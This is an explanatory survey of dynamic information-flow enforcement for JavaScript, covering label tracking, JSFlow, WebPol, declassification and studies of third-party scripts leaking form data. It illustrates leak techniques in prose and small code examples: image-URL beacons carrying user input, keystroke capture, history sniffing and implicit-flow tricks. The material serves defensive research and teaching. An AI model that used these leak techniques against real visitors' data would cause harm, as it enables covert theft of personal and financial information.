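# Dynamic information-flow enforcement for JavaScript and web browsers in practice

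## Why browsers need to track data after a script has read it

Dynamic information-flow enforcement protects secret data in a running program. It tracks each piece of data as the program copies it, computes with it and makes decisions based on it, and intervenes when the data is about to be sent somewhere it isn't allowed to go. Since the late 2000s, researchers have applied the method to JavaScript, the language of the scripts that web pages run in visitors' browsers. Most pages run some code that their owners did not write, and browsers control what such code may read much better than what it does with the data afterwards.

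### A loan calculator and its guest

*Information-flow security for JavaScript and its APIs* (Hedin, Bello and Sabelfeld, 2016) gives the example of a page that calculates loan repayments. The visitor enters a monthly income and an amount to borrow, and a script computes the instalments. If the owner also wants to know how many people use the page and where they give up, the usual solution is to add a script tag that loads an analytics script from another company.

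The browser fetches the file and runs it "with the privileges of the document", as the internet standard *The Web Origin Concept* (Barth, 2011) puts it. The analytics script can therefore do whatever the page's own script can. It can read the income field through the DOM (Document Object Model), the browser's live representation of the page, which scripts can read and change. It can also collect the income digit by digit, before the visitor clicks any button, by registering an event handler, a function that the browser calls when an event such as a key press occurs.

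Most popular websites include scripts from other servers. Nikiforakis, Invernizzi and colleagues (2012), in *You Are What You Include*, crawled more than three million pages of the 10,000 most popular websites and found that 88.45% of the sites included at least one script from a remote server. Some sites relied on as many as 295 different hosts. The Web Almanac's *Third Parties* (2025) found third-party content on more than nine pages in ten, with scripts among the most common types of request. Third parties often load other third parties, so a page may run code that its owner never chose.

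A script can misuse the data it reads either because attackers have taken over its supplier or because the supplier designed it to collect what people type. In December 2011, attackers broke into the site that distributed qTip2, a popular plugin, and the site served a malicious version for 33 days, according to Nikiforakis and colleagues. In *Tracker Installations Are Not Created Equal*, Kieserman, Andreou and colleagues (2025) examined 40,150 websites and found Meta's tracking script on 28.2% of them. The setting for collecting form data was switched on in 62.3% of those installations. The share was lower on finance sites, at 20.3%, but it still matters because those pages ask about money.

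In *Every Keystroke You Make*, Munir, Demir and colleagues (2025) filled in forms on a sample of 15,000 sites without submitting them. On at least 3.18% of the sites, a third-party script that listened for keystrokes sent the typed text to a third party's server. This is a lower bound because the researchers could recognise their test data only in the encodings they searched for.

Real loan sites have done much the same as the imagined one. The Markup tested more than 700 lenders' websites for *Mortgage Brokers Sent People’s Estimated Credit, Address, and Veteran Status to Facebook* (2024) and found that over 200 shared some data with Facebook through Meta's script. The script on Veterans United Home Loans' loan calculator told Facebook whether visitors owned a home and which branch of the military they had served in. Only a handful of the sites tracked detailed personal and financial information,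 and most shared far less.

### What the same-origin policy leaves open

The browser's main defence is the same-origin policy, which generally prevents content from one origin from reading content from another. An origin is the combination of a scheme (such as http or https), a host name and a port. The policy stops a hostile page in one tab from reading a bank statement open in another.

The same-origin policy does not protect the income field from the analytics script. A script runs under the origin of the page that includes it, whichever server it came from, so the analytics script has the same origin as the field and may read it. The script can also send the number to another server, because browsers restrict reading across origins but broadly allow sending. W3C's page *Same Origin Policy* explains that a ban on sending would also ban links from one site to another, and that the web would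 not exist without those links.

The script can then leak the visitor's income with a single line of code. It creates an image and sets its address to one on the analytics company's server, with the income added to the end. The browser requests the image, and the server records the address whether or not it sends back a picture.

Yang, Stefan and colleagues, in *Toward Principled Browser Security*, describe the same-origin policy as already an information-flow policy, though a very restrictive one to which browsers have added many exceptions. In its strict form, it would forbid every flow between origins. The exceptions allow images, scripts, style sheets, frames and outgoing requests. Removing them would stop the image trick, but the researchers concede that nobody would want to use the resulting browser.

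One of two tools site owners can use to tighten security is Content Security Policy, a header that lists the servers from which a page may load resources. Yang and colleagues point out that this list also limits where the page can leak data. It would stop a hijacked script from sending the income to an unknown server. But the list applies to the whole page. The analytics company must be on it for the analytics to work, and scripts on the page can then send that company the income as easily as a count of page views.

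The other tool is the iframe, a page embedded in the main page with its own origin. A script from another origin in an iframe cannot read the loan form, but it cannot read the rest of the surrounding page either, so it has very little to analyse. The owner therefore has to choose between fully integrating a script and isolating it. Hedin and colleagues judge iframes a good fit for stand-alone services, such as advertisements that do not depend on the page's content, but inadequate for statistics, utility libraries and advertisements that match the page.

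### Permission to read settles too little

Both tools are forms of access control, meaning they decide which code may reach which resource. If the code that computes the instalments comes from a third party, access control can't protect the income without breaking the calculator. The code needs to read the income to do the computation, and once it has permission to do so, it can send the income anywhere the page can.

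Hedin and colleagues give a second example, in which the data is text copied from an article rather than form data. Some newspaper sites include a third-party script that adds a link to the article whenever a reader copies a passage. The script must read the selected text, change it and write it back to the clipboard. Once it has read the text, it can also send the copied passage to its maker.

The calculator's owner would like to restrict how the visitor's income is used. It may go into the figure on the screen, and perhaps to the lender's own server if the visitor is a customer there, but nowhere else. To enforce this rule, the browser has to track the income after the script has read it.

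### Labels, flows and a three-line leak

A *source* is a place where sensitive data enters a script, such as a form field or a cookie. A *sink* is a place where data can leave, such as a network request or an image address. A *label* is a tag on a value that records how secret the value is, or which origins have influenced it. The simplest policy has two levels, *high* for secret and *low* for public, and forbids high data from reaching low sinks. In the examples below, the variable h starts high and the others start low.

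An *explicit flow* occurs when a program copies data or computes directly from it, as in `l = h`. In this easy case, the mechanism copies the label along with the value, so `l` becomes high and an attempt to put `l` into an image address fails.

Following explicit flows alone goes by the name of *taint tracking*. According to Hedin and Sabelfeld, in *Web Application Security using JSFlow*, it has proved useful where an attacker controls the input to a program but not the program itself. A hostile third-party script is the program, and its author can avoid copying anything:

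```
if (h) { l = 1; } else { l = 0; }
```

Afterwards l matches h, although no statement copies h into l. This is an *implicit flow*, in which the choice of branch reveals the information. A script can copy the visitor's entire income by repeating this for each binary digit of the number.

To catch it, the mechanism keeps one more label, the *program-counter label* or *pc*, which covers everything that determined whether the current instruction runs. The pc is high inside both branches above because the value of h determines which one runs. An obvious fix is to make every variable that the script writes under a high pc high as well. Here l would become high in either case, which would seem to close the leak.

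It is not, and Hedin and colleagues show why with three lines. Assume that h is either 1 or 0.

```
l = 1; t = 0;
if (h == 1) { t = 1; }
if (t != 1) { l = 0; }
```

If h is 1, the second line sets t to 1 and marks it high. The test on the third line then fails, and l is still 1 and low. If h is 0, t remains 0 and low, and the test on the third line succeeds. The pc is low because the test depends only on t, so l stays low when the script sets it to 0. In both cases l ends up equal to h but is labeled public, so the script can send it.

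The problem is t, whose label depends on the secret. Austin and Flanagan, in *Permissive Dynamic Information Flow Analysis*, call a variable partially leaked when it holds private data but its label is private on one execution and public on another. The *no-sensitive-upgrade rule* prevents this by stopping a script that tries to write to a low variable under a high pc. In the example, it stops the script on the second line, when h is 1 and the script tries to change t. With a check for such cases, Austin and Flanagan (2009), in *Efficient purely-dynamic information flow analysis*, could track flows in JavaScript-like languages entirely at runtime and still guarantee *noninterference*, the property that secret inputs cannot change public outputs.

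The guarantee usually compares only the outputs of runs that terminate, so a script can still leak information through whether it finishes (a termination channel) or when (a timing channel). In the three-line program, the mechanism halts the script when h is 1 and lets it finish when h is 0, so anyone waiting for its message learns the secret bit. In *Termination-Insensitive Noninterference Leaks More Than Just a Bit*, Askarov, Hunt and colleagues describe this gap as the tradeoff for a reasonably permissive rule, and it can leak more than one bit.

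The rule can also stop harmless scripts. If the third line were missing and nothing used t again, the program would leak nothing through t, but the rule would still stop it. Such a *false stop* can break a website.

### Why not check the script before it runs?

An analysis that inspects a program in advance can examine both branches of a condition, including the one that does not run. Tools like this exist for other languages, such as Jif for Java, but they are poorly suited to JavaScript.

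Much of a page's code can't be inspected in advance because scripts create it as they run. A script can assemble text and run it as code, for instance with the function eval, or write a new script tag into the page. Nikiforakis and colleagues reproduce a snippet for loading Google Analytics that builds a script tag from pieces of text, choosing one of two server addresses depending on whether the page came over a secure connection. They couldn't count the scripts on a page just by downloading it, so they had to execute each page in a simulated browser and observe what it requested.

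Types and labels also change as the program runs. A variable can hold a number now and an object later, and two variables, x and y, can refer to the same object. If a script then stores the income in a property of y, the same property of x also becomes secret. A static analysis must determine before the program runs that x and y refer to the same object. A runtime mechanism stores the label in the object itself, so the label is found through either variable.

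Scripts can add and delete an object's properties, so the existence of a property can reveal information even when its value doesn't. In the program `o = {}; if (h) { o.q = 0; }`, the value of q is always 0, but checking whether q exists reveals whether h is true.

### Monitors and multi-execution

There are two main kinds of runtime enforcement. One is a *monitor*, which tracks labels during a single execution and blocks forbidden flows, usually with the no-sensitive-upgrade rule or a refinement of it. A monitor has to handle nearly every operation, so it is hard to combine with the JIT compiler, the part of a JavaScript engine that turns frequently run code into fast machine code.

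*Secure multi-execution* runs the script once per security level and gives each run only the inputs that its level permits. The run that sends data to the analytics server receives a dummy value instead of the income, so it cannot leak the income, whichever branches it takes.

Most of the browser systems date from a period of about ten years. Hedin and Sabelfeld list many of them:

- **2007:** Vogt and colleagues modify Firefox to track sensitive data and crawl about a million websites with it. After they set aside 30 sites by hand, it flags suspected transfers to other domains on 1.35% of the sites.
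- **2009:** Mozilla starts FlowSafe, a project to build runtime tracking into Firefox. BFlow tracks data between the frames of a page. Chugh, Meister and colleagues (2009), in *Staged Information Flow for JavaScript*, analyse what they can in advance and leave checks for code that arrives later.
- **2012:** FlowFox brings secure multi-execution to Firefox.
- **2013 to 2016:** Hedin and colleagues develop JSFlow, an interpreter that carries labels through the full language of its day.
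- **2014:** Bichhawat and colleagues put a monitor inside the JavaScript engine of WebKit, the browser engine behind Safari.

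## Writing the policy for a page

Somebody has to write a policy before a monitor or a multi-execution browser can enforce it. The policy names the sources that hold sensitive data and the sinks that the data may reach. The loan calculator's rule for the income won't suit every page, and it isn't obvious who should write the policy.

### Four policies for popular websites

Jang, Jhala and colleagues (2010), in *An Empirical Study of Privacy-Violating Information Flows in JavaScript Web Applications*, wrote policies against four kinds of misuse. They tested popular websites with a modified version of Chrome that rewrote each script so that it carried labels. Each policy combines a rule that attaches a label with a rule that blocks it. To protect the cookie of a site called a.com, the rules are:

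```
at document.cookie inject "secret"
at $1.x = $2 if $1.url ≠ "a.com" block "secret" on $2
```

The first rule labels whatever a script reads from the cookie. In the second, `$1` stands for any object and `$2` for any value. This rule stops the program before it stores a secret value in an object that another site's script created.

The other three policies follow the same pattern:

- **Location hijacking:** third-party code changes the address that the page is about to open. The policy labels values from third-party code "untrusted" and keeps them out of that address.
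- **History sniffing:** browsers show visited links in a different colour, so a script can create hidden links, read their colours and learn where the visitor has been. The policy labels the style of a link and blocks it at the network.
- **Behaviour tracking:** a script records clicks, mouse movements or copied text. The policy labels these events and blocks them at the network.

The researchers looked only at front pages, and they ran only the history policy on all 50,000 sites.

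| Misuse | Sites checked | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Cookie stealing | 100 | 17 to 48 sites, depending on what counts as another site |
| Location hijacking | 100 | none |
| History sniffing | 50,000 | 63 flagged, 46 confirmed by hand |
| Behaviour tracking | 1,300 | 328 flagged, 115 left after filtering |

The number of sites that broke the cookie policy depended on which hosts counted as another site. When any different host name counted, 48 of the 100 sites broke the policy. Treating all hosts in one domain as the same site reduced the number to 38. It fell to 17 when the researchers also trusted every outside site that at least three of the 100 sites used, mostly statistics and advertising companies. They confirmed by hand that every flow was real, but a real flow may still be acceptable. Facebook, for instance, loaded most of its scripts from fbcdn.net, which all three definitions treated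 as a different site.

History sniffing is easier to judge because a visitor has little reason to want it. One of the 46 sites confirmed to do it was among the world's 100 most popular, and 36 used code from two companies. (The paper's conclusion gives the total as 43 instead of 46.) Of the 17 other flagged sites, 12 had code too complicated for the researchers to understand, and five showed no suspicious network traffic. The tool also missed some flows, including those through the DOM, so the true number may be higher.

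The policy for behaviour tracking could not distinguish spying from ordinary page design. Many sites send a request when the mouse passes over a small picture, to fetch a larger one. Jang and colleagues therefore discarded cases in which the server sent back more than 100 bytes, assuming that a hidden tracker gets little in reply. They examined the ten most popular of the remaining 115 sites and found covert tracking on seven.

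### Three kinds of loan calculator

Hedin and colleagues studied far fewer pages in more depth. In September 2013 they ran loan calculators in Firefox, with JSFlow replacing its JavaScript engine. Their baseline policy stopped pages from sending anything derived from the visitor's input to another origin, including in an image URL.

The calculators fell into three classes. Some, such as the one from the British bank Halifax, did all the arithmetic in the browser. These worked even under a stricter policy that let no user data leave the browser and so blocked form submission. Others, such as TD Canada Trust's, sent the input to their own server, so they worked under the baseline policy but not the stricter one. The rest shared the input with third parties, or let third-party scripts read it, and needed a policy looser than both.

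Calculators in the first two classes could keep using Google Analytics. JSFlow tracked data through Google's script and allowed the script's requests as long as they contained nothing derived from the input.

The site mlcalc.com, in the third class, leaked the visitor's input through its own server, where a browser monitor cannot track it. The browser first submitted the visitor's figures to mlcalc.com, which the baseline policy allowed. The server then returned a page containing a script that logged the same figures to Google Analytics. By then the figures no longer carried a label showing that they came from the visitor. JSFlow lets a server restore the label with an *upgrade annotation*, an added instruction that raises a label in advance, but this only works if the site cooperates. The server could also send the figures directly to another company, which a browser monitor could not detect.

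Hedin and colleagues also tested a copy-and-paste script from Tynt, a company whose customers included the Financial Times. The script added a link to the copied text. It also requested an image from tynt.com and sent the text with that request, along with a cookie that identified the reader across all sites using Tynt. JSFlow treated the selected text as secret and stopped the script with a security error when it tried to send the text. Three years earlier, Jang and colleagues had found Tynt's script sending copied text from seven sites.

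### What the labels can express

Two levels are enough for a rule such as "nothing typed here leaves the browser". A policy that lets the income go to the lender but lets another value go only to the analytics company needs labels that name origins.

*First-Class Labels*, by Hennigan, Kerschbaumer and colleagues, gives each value a set of names. The browser automatically adds the origin of the script or resource, and developers can add names of their own, such as "pwd" for a password. The result of a computation carries the names of all its inputs. The developer writes a function to check that each outgoing request carries only names from a permitted set.

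Hennigan and colleagues added labels named by the developer because automatic labels alone produce too many reports, including reports of routine requests that involve content distribution servers. They meant the system for testing a site before release, not for protecting its visitors. The system has no way to remove a label, so hostile code can't remove one.

In WebPol, which Bichhawat, Rajani and colleagues (2017), in *WebPol*, built on their monitor for WebKit, a label names the place where a value may go. There are three kinds, in rising order of secrecy:

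public < *domain* < local

Public data may go anywhere. Data with a domain's label may go only to that domain's servers, and local data may never leave the browser. If a script combines data labeled for two unrelated domains, the result must be labeled local, because no other label is above both.

### A WebPol policy step by step

A WebPol policy is a JavaScript file that the site's developer includes in the page's HTML. All data starts out public, and the policy raises the labels of particular page elements. On the loan page, one line could label the income field `HOST`, which stands for the page's own domain. The analytics script could still read the income but no longer send it to the script's maker.

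Policies can also change as the visitor uses the page. Suppose a developer wants an analytics company to learn whether a visitor clicked in some section of the page, but not where or how often. Bichhawat and colleagues give a policy for this, shown here with one correction:

```
var alreadyClicked = false;
var p = document.getElementById("sect_name");
p.addEventListener("click", function (event) {
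  if (alreadyClicked) { event.setContext("HOST"); }
  else { alreadyClicked = true; event.setLabel("HOST"); }
});
```

The browser runs this function on every click in the section, before any other script can respond. On the first click, `setLabel` makes the event's details, such as its coordinates, private to the site. The analytics script still runs and can report that a click happened. On every later click, `setContext` raises the pc for all the functions that respond to the click. Whatever the analytics script then writes or sends carries the `HOST` label, so the script can't report the click to its own server.

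The correction is in the fourth line, where the published version has `alreadyClicked = true` as the condition. In JavaScript, this sets the variable instead of testing it, so the condition always holds and the policy hides the first click as well. This mistake makes the policy too strict, but a similar one elsewhere could release a secret.

Only policy files in the page's HTML can set labels, and third-party scripts cannot move or detach an element that has a policy. WebPol trusts the site's own code completely. A hostile script might still lay a transparent field over the password box and trick the visitor into typing in that field, which no policy covers. To counter this, Bichhawat and colleagues add a policy that labels all key presses in elements that are more than half transparent.

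A policy sometimes has to label more than the sources. In the WebPol policy for passwordmeter.com, a real site that rates passwords, two lines label the password fields. The policy needs four more lines to label every `div` element on the page, so that the script can display a score computed from the password.

Six students tried to write policies for four small pages, with up to an hour to read the instructions and do the work. All six completed three of the exercises, but only the two who had studied information flow before completed the fourth, which required `setContext`. The group is too small to show much about developers in general, but the difficulty is plausible because hiding that an event happened is a less familiar idea than hiding a password.

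### Releasing part of a secret

The click policy releases one fact about the visitor's behaviour. If clicks are secret, strict noninterference forbids even this, because the public output would depend on a secret input. Such a deliberate, permitted release is called *declassification*.

*Stateful Declassification Policies for Event-Driven Programs* (Vanhoef, De Groef and colleagues, 2014) compares two scripts that listen to the keyboard. One sends every key press to an attacker. The other waits until the visitor leaves the page and then reports whether they ever used a certain keyboard shortcut. Noninterference rules out both, although a site owner could reasonably want the second.

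Their policies consist of two functions. A *projection* function determines what the public side receives when each event arrives. It can pass on a rounded version of the visitor's location or hide the event completely. A *release* function keeps track of earlier events and publishes a summary of them. For the shortcut, the public value starts at 0 and changes to 1 the first time the visitor presses the key. Another release function publishes the average mouse position after every 100 clicks.

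This leads to a weaker form of noninterference. Let I be a list of input events and D\*(I) everything that the policy D allows the public side to learn from them. It contains each projected event, together with the released value at that moment. A program is secure under D if, for any two lists I and I′,

D\*(I) = D\*(I′) implies that the public outputs are the same.

The release policy treats a visit in which the user pressed the shortcut once the same as one in which they pressed it five times, so the script must send the same message after both. The message may differ if the user never pressed it. A policy that hides every secret event and releases nothing gives ordinary noninterference.

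Vanhoef and colleagues enforce these policies in FlowFox, where the public run of a script never receives the key presses. To get the result, the script calls a function named `declassify`. In the public run, this function ignores its argument and returns the value that the policy has released, so a hostile script that calls `declassify(password)` gets only the 0 or 1. A benign script must also make the call, or its public run will always report 0. Existing scripts therefore need changes before they can use a release function, whereas those that already stay within a projection policy run unmodified.

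The proofs cover a small model language, not the whole browser. The researchers also acknowledge that a policy written as a program can be hard to read, so its author may release more information than intended. Their policies can't single out the key presses typed into a credit-card form, because only the page's own code identifies that form. WebPol can, because the developer attaches the policy to the form itself.

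Declassification can also allow harmless flows that have nothing to do with statistics. Hedin and colleagues found two scripts that checked early on whether the user's input was null, meaning no value was present. Nothing the user did could make the check fail, but it caused much of what the scripts computed afterwards to become secret. The researchers added declassification annotations by hand to let these flows through.

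When data belongs to several parties, someone also has to decide whose permission is needed to release it. *Decentralized Delimited Release* proposes a framework that releases combined data only if all of its owners agree.

### Browser vendor, site or user

A browser vendor can protect every visitor at once, and some rules suit almost every page. *Protecting Sensitive Data in Web Browsers with ScriptPolice* describes a version of Chrome with a few standard policies built in, mainly to control browser extensions. Vanhoef and colleagues suggest that browsers could offer simple policies, such as rounding the visitor's location, as part of a privacy profile. But a vendor doesn't know which field on a page holds an income or which outside servers belong to the site. Netscape added data tainting to its browser in the 1990s but later abandoned it, partly because it raised too many alerts, according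 to Jang and colleagues.

Users know what they want to keep private, but few could write a policy, and Vanhoef and colleagues call it unrealistic to expect them to. For policies specific to one application, they proposed that the site write the rules and send them to the browser. Bichhawat and colleagues describe Vanhoef's policies as managed by the user, which does not match this proposal. A user could more realistically approve individual releases of information, as in Mash-IF, an earlier system that Bichhawat and colleagues discuss.

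The site's developer knows the page best and chooses which scripts to include, so WebPol and W3C's *Confinement with Origin Web Labels* rely on the developer to write the policy. In the latter, a site can mark a password as confidential before handing it to another company's strength checker. This works well when the site and its visitors want the same thing, as when a bank and its customers both want to keep passwords away from the bank's analytics supplier.

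A policy written by a site's owner does not protect visitors if the site shares their data on purpose. The owner of a calculator like mlcalc.com could write a policy that permits the sharing. Visitors who also want protection from the site would need the strictest policy that Hedin and colleagues tried, and only calculators that do all their arithmetic in the browser would still work under it.

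## Tracking labels through JavaScript in a custom interpreter

To protect the loan calculator's visitor, the label on the income must stay attached however a script uses the income. A script can pass on information in many ways without copying it, some of which don't involve a visible `if`. JSFlow, the interpreter from the loan-calculator tests, is designed to catch them all. Hedin, Birgisson and colleagues (2014) introduced it in *JSFlow*, and Hedin and colleagues gave the full account two years later.

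### A JavaScript interpreter in JavaScript

The developers wrote JSFlow in about 12,000 lines of JavaScript. It runs all of ECMAScript 5, the 2009 edition of the language standard, except strict mode, which is optional and forbids some older features. Few sites used strict mode at the time, and strict code can also run under the ordinary rules.

The alternative was to modify an existing engine, such as V8 in Chrome or SpiderMonkey in Firefox. Those engines change quickly, and their developers concentrate on speed. An interpreter written in JavaScript took less effort and can run in a browser extension, in a proxy between the browser and the web, in a library that a site adds to its own pages, or on a server. But JSFlow is far slower than a browser's own engine.

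To run JSFlow on real pages, Hedin and colleagues built Snowfox, an experimental Firefox extension that passes each page's scripts to JSFlow as the page loads. When a script breaks the policy, the extension can log the leak, silently block the request or stop the script. The version that Hedin and Sabelfeld used for a tutorial stops the script and shows an alert, and the user decides whether to allow the flow.

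A label in JSFlow is a set of origins. By default, whatever the visitor enters carries the label `user`, and everything else is public. Each sink also has a label, which limits how secret the data it receives may be.

A sink can be a single web address instead of a whole domain. For their tutorial, Hedin and Sabelfeld wrote a deliberately insecure forum called Hrafn, with a policy that lets the password go only to the login address. In one of their attacks, a malicious article contains a script that creates a new forum post with the user name and password of anyone who logs in. A policy that named only domains would allow this, because the password never leaves Hrafn's domain. JSFlow stops the script because the address for new posts isn't the login address.

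The following examples again use two labels, high and low. Unless noted otherwise, h starts high and everything else starts low.

### Reading and writing a property

A JavaScript object is a collection of named properties, and `o[p]` refers to the property of o whose name is the value of p. Even a plain read can therefore leak a secret:

```
o = { a: 0, b: 1 };
x = o[p];
```

Suppose p is high and holds either "a" or "b". Both stored numbers are low, but x reveals which name p held. The label of x must therefore include everything that the script used to reach the property. Hedin and colleagues call this the *read context*. For `o[p]` it consists of the label of o, which covers the choice of object, and the label of p. With ⊔ for the operation that combines labels (the result is high if any part is high), the rule is:

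label of x = label of the stored value ⊔ label of o ⊔ label of p

A write has to take the pc into account as well:

```
if (c) { o[p] = y; }
```

The *write context* is pc ⊔ the label of o ⊔ the label of p, and inside this branch the pc includes the label of c. JSFlow allows the write only if the property's current value has a label at least as high as the write context. The new value's label is then the label of y ⊔ the write context.

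JSFlow extends the no-sensitive-upgrade rule from branches to names and references. Suppose `o.a` and `o.b` are both 0 and low, and `p` is high. `o[p] = 1` changes one of them, so reading `o.a` afterwards reveals what `p` was. JSFlow stops the script at the write, even though there is no branch and the pc is low.

The check does not depend on the label of y. When the write context is low, a script may store a secret in a low property, which makes the property high, or overwrite a secret with a public value, which makes the property low again. Neither label change depends on a secret.

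### Raising a label before the branch

The same rule causes false stops, as in this harmless program:

```
l = false;
if (h) { l = true; }
```

JSFlow halts it when h is true. One upgrade annotation rescues it:

```
l = upg false to h;
if (h) { l = true; }
```

The expression `upg false to h` evaluates to false with the label of `h`. The variable `l` is already high when the branch begins, so the write is legal. `l` is high whether `h` is true or false, so its label reveals nothing about `h`.

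The annotation copies the label of another value, h, because a fixed label proved inflexible in practice. When labels are sets of origins, a programmer often can't know in advance which origins h will carry. Other forms of the annotation raise the labels JSFlow keeps for objects, exceptions and jumps.

A hostile script can contain upgrade annotations too, but they don't help it. Hedin and Sabelfeld, in *Information-Flow Security for a Core of JavaScript* (2012), add two of them to the three-line leak from the introduction. In the later notation, the program becomes:

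```
l = 1; t = upg 0 to h;
if (h == 1) { t = 1; }
l = upg l to t;
if (t != 1) { l = 0; }
```

The program now runs to the end for both values of h, and l still ends up equal to h. But l is high, so the script can't send it. A badly placed annotation can make too much data secret and so break a page, but it can't release anything.

Existing websites contain no such annotations, so a person or a tool has to add them. Hedin and Sabelfeld experimented with automatic testing on a small language with records and exceptions. A tool ran each program on generated inputs, and whenever the monitor stopped the program, the tool used the trace to find where an upgrade was missing. For their tests on real pages, Hedin and colleagues used a proxy to insert annotations into the scripts before they reached the browser.

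### Properties that exist only sometimes

In `o = {}; if (h) { o.q = 0; }`, whether `o` has a property `q` reveals whether `h` is true. A label on the value of `q` can't prevent this leak, because when `h` is false there is no `q` to label.

JSFlow therefore gives every property an *existence label* and every object a *structure label*. A script may add a property only if the object's structure label is at least as high as the write context, and the new property's existence label is then equal to the write context. In the example, the structure of o is low, so JSFlow stops the script when h is true. With an upgrade, the script can continue:

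```
o = {}; upgs o to h;
if (h) { o.q = 0; }
l = (o.q != undefined);
```

Here `upgs` raises the structure label of o. The last line tests whether q exists, because JavaScript returns undefined for a missing property. If q exists, the result takes q's existence label, and if q is missing, it takes o's structure label. Both labels are high, so l is high in either case.

A high structure label does not make the whole object secret. If the script later adds a property outside any secret branch, that property has a low existence label, and the script can read it and send its value as usual.

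Deleting a property under a high pc requires the object's structure label and the property's existence label to be high. A script that deletes either o.x or o.y, depending on h, must first raise the structure label of o and the existence labels of both properties.

Loops over an object's properties need similar care:

```
n = 0;
for (x in o) { n = n + 1; }
```

If o has a property whose existence is secret, the final count is secret too. JSFlow runs the loop body once for each property, with the pc raised to that property's existence label. When the loop body tries to write to n during the secret property's iteration, JSFlow stops the script. If the script continues past a secret property, the pc can drop again for the next one, because the secret iteration could not have had any public effect.

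These rules are precise, but they can require many annotations. Hedin and Sabelfeld consider a shopping cart in which third-party advertisements appear in the same list as the customer's items, and the merchant wants to hide whether the customer gets a discount. The line `if (h) { ul.appendChild(D); }` adds the discount `D` to the list `ul` when `h` is true. This call requires seven upgrades because it changes the list's array of elements, the array's length and several links between neighbouring elements.

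### Leaving a block early

An exception is JavaScript's way of abandoning the current code when something goes wrong. It can leak a secret through code that comes after a branch:

```
l = true;
if (h) { throw 0; }
l = false;
```

The last line is outside the branch, so the pc is low there. But that line runs only if h is false, so l ends up equal to h. Hedin and Sabelfeld reject having the monitor treat everything after a possible secret exception as secret, which they consider too restrictive because most of those exceptions never happen.

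Instead, JSFlow keeps an *exception label*, which limits where a script may throw an exception. While the label is low, JSFlow stops the script if it reaches a `throw` under a high pc, so the last line can safely remain public. The script may throw there if it first raises the exception label, but from then on the label is part of every write context, so JSFlow treats every later write as a write under a secret.

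A `try` block, which catches exceptions from the code inside it, limits how long this lasts:

```
l1 = upg true to h;
try {
  upg exc to h;
  if (h) { throw 0; }
  l1 = false;
} catch (e) { }
l2 = 16;
```

The line `l1 = false` runs only if h is false, so l1 must already be high. The line `l2 = 16` runs in either case. JSFlow restores the old exception label at the end of the `try` statement, so l2 stays low. Code in the `catch` block would run under a high pc, because it runs only if the exception occurred.

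A script can cause an exception without a `throw` statement, for instance by reading a variable that doesn't exist. JSFlow checks these exceptions against the exception label too.

An early return has the same effect as an exception:

```
l = true;
function f() {
  if (h) { return 1; }
  l = false;
}
f();
```

So does a jump out of the middle of a block:

```
l = true;
L1: do {
  if (h) { continue L1; }
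  l = false;
} while (false);
```

JSFlow keeps a *return label* and a separate label for each place a script can jump to, such as L1. These work like the exception label. While the relevant label is low, a script can't return or jump from a secret branch. Once the script has raised it, JSFlow treats the writes that the return or jump could have skipped as secret.

Ordinary scripts often return from the middle of functions, and they contain no annotations to raise the return label. Bichhawat and colleagues (2014), who built the monitor for WebKit, list slowness and the extra annotations for exceptions and returns among the drawbacks of custom interpreters.

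### Functions, prototypes and scopes

JavaScript programs can store functions in variables, so a secret can decide which function a later line calls. In this program, f starts high:

```
if (h) { f = function () { l = 1; }; }
else   { f = function () { l = 0; }; }
f();
```

The call is outside the branch, and each function writes only a constant. JSFlow prevents this leak by labeling f like any other value and running its body with the pc raised to that label. The write to l therefore happens under a high pc, and JSFlow stops it.

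Looking up a property can also reveal a secret, because objects inherit properties. If an object lacks a property, JavaScript looks for it in another object called its prototype, then in the prototype's prototype, and so on. A simplified version of an example from Hedin and colleagues uses a chain of three objects:

```
a = { v: 0 };
b = Object.create(a);
x = Object.create(b);
if (h) { b.v = 1; }
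r = x.v;
```

The object x inherits from b, which inherits from a. If h is true, the search for v ends at b and returns 1. Otherwise it continues to a and returns 0.

The existing labels are enough here. The script can add v to b under a high pc only if it has already raised b's structure label. During the search, JSFlow collects the structure label of each object that lacks the property, so the result gets b's high structure label if v is missing from b, and v's high existence label if it is there.

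Variables work in much the same way. JavaScript looks for a variable in the current function first, then in the code around it and finally among the global variables. The `with` statement places an ordinary object at the front of this chain:

```
o = {};
if (h) { o.l = 1; }
with (o) { l = 0; }
```

The last line changes o.l if h is true and the outer l if h is false. JSFlow represents each step of the chain as an object, so the existing rules apply. If the script has raised the structure label of o so that it can add the property, the search for l picks up that high label as it passes through o, and JSFlow blocks the write to the outer l when h is false. Code run through `eval` can hide a variable in the same way, by declaring another one with the same name.

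### Branches inside the interpreter

Some leaks have no secret branch in the script that decides whether a public write happens. JavaScript often converts values from one type to another automatically. To add 1 to an object, it first calls the object's `valueOf` function. If that returns another object instead of a simple value such as a number, JavaScript calls `toString`. Scripts can define both functions:

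```
l = false;
x = {
  valueOf:  function () { return h ? {} : 1; },
  toString: function () { l = true; return 1; }
};
n = x + 1;
```

If h is true, `valueOf` returns an object, so JavaScript then calls `toString`, which sets l to true. If h is false, `toString` doesn't run. The check that determines whether to call it happens inside the interpreter, during the addition.

JSFlow therefore applies the idea of a pc to its own code. It keeps a stack of labels instead of a single pc because the interpreter can be inside several branches at once, each ending at a different point. When the interpreter branches on a labeled value, it pushes the value's label onto the stack, and it pops the label when the alternatives rejoin. JSFlow checks every write against the combination of all the labels on the stack.

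In the example, the result of `valueOf` is high because it depends on h. The interpreter has to test whether this result is an object, so it puts a high label on the stack before calling `toString`. When `toString` tries to write to l, JSFlow stops the script.

The function that converts values to numbers shows how this looks in the interpreter. In simplified form:

```
function toNumber(x) {
  if (!isObject(x.value)) {
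    return labeled(Number(x.value), x.label);
  }
  pushPC(x.label);
  var prim = toPrimitive(x);
  popPC();
  return labeled(Number(prim.value), prim.label);
}
```

Inside JSFlow, x is a pair of a value and a label. If the value isn't an object, the function converts it and keeps the label. If it is an object, `toPrimitive` may call functions from the script, and those calls reveal that x held an object. The function therefore puts the label of x on the stack for the duration of the call.

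An `if` in the script also makes the interpreter choose what to run next, so it adds a label to the stack in the same way. The ordinary pc is thus a special case. Hedin and colleagues point out that every flow in a script comes from a flow in the interpreter that runs it. A developer can therefore look for hidden flows in an operation by checking where the interpreter's own code branches on a labeled value.

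The library functions that come with JavaScript need the same treatment, and models of them make up around 30% of JSFlow's code.

### What the theorems cover

Hedin and colleagues proved two theorems about a core of JavaScript. The noninterference theorem concerns two runs of the same program that start in states that look the same to an observer who can see only low data. In such states, the labels match, the low values are equal, and objects with a low structure label have the same properties. If both runs terminate, their final states also look the same to that observer. This holds for every program in the core language, including programs written by an attacker.

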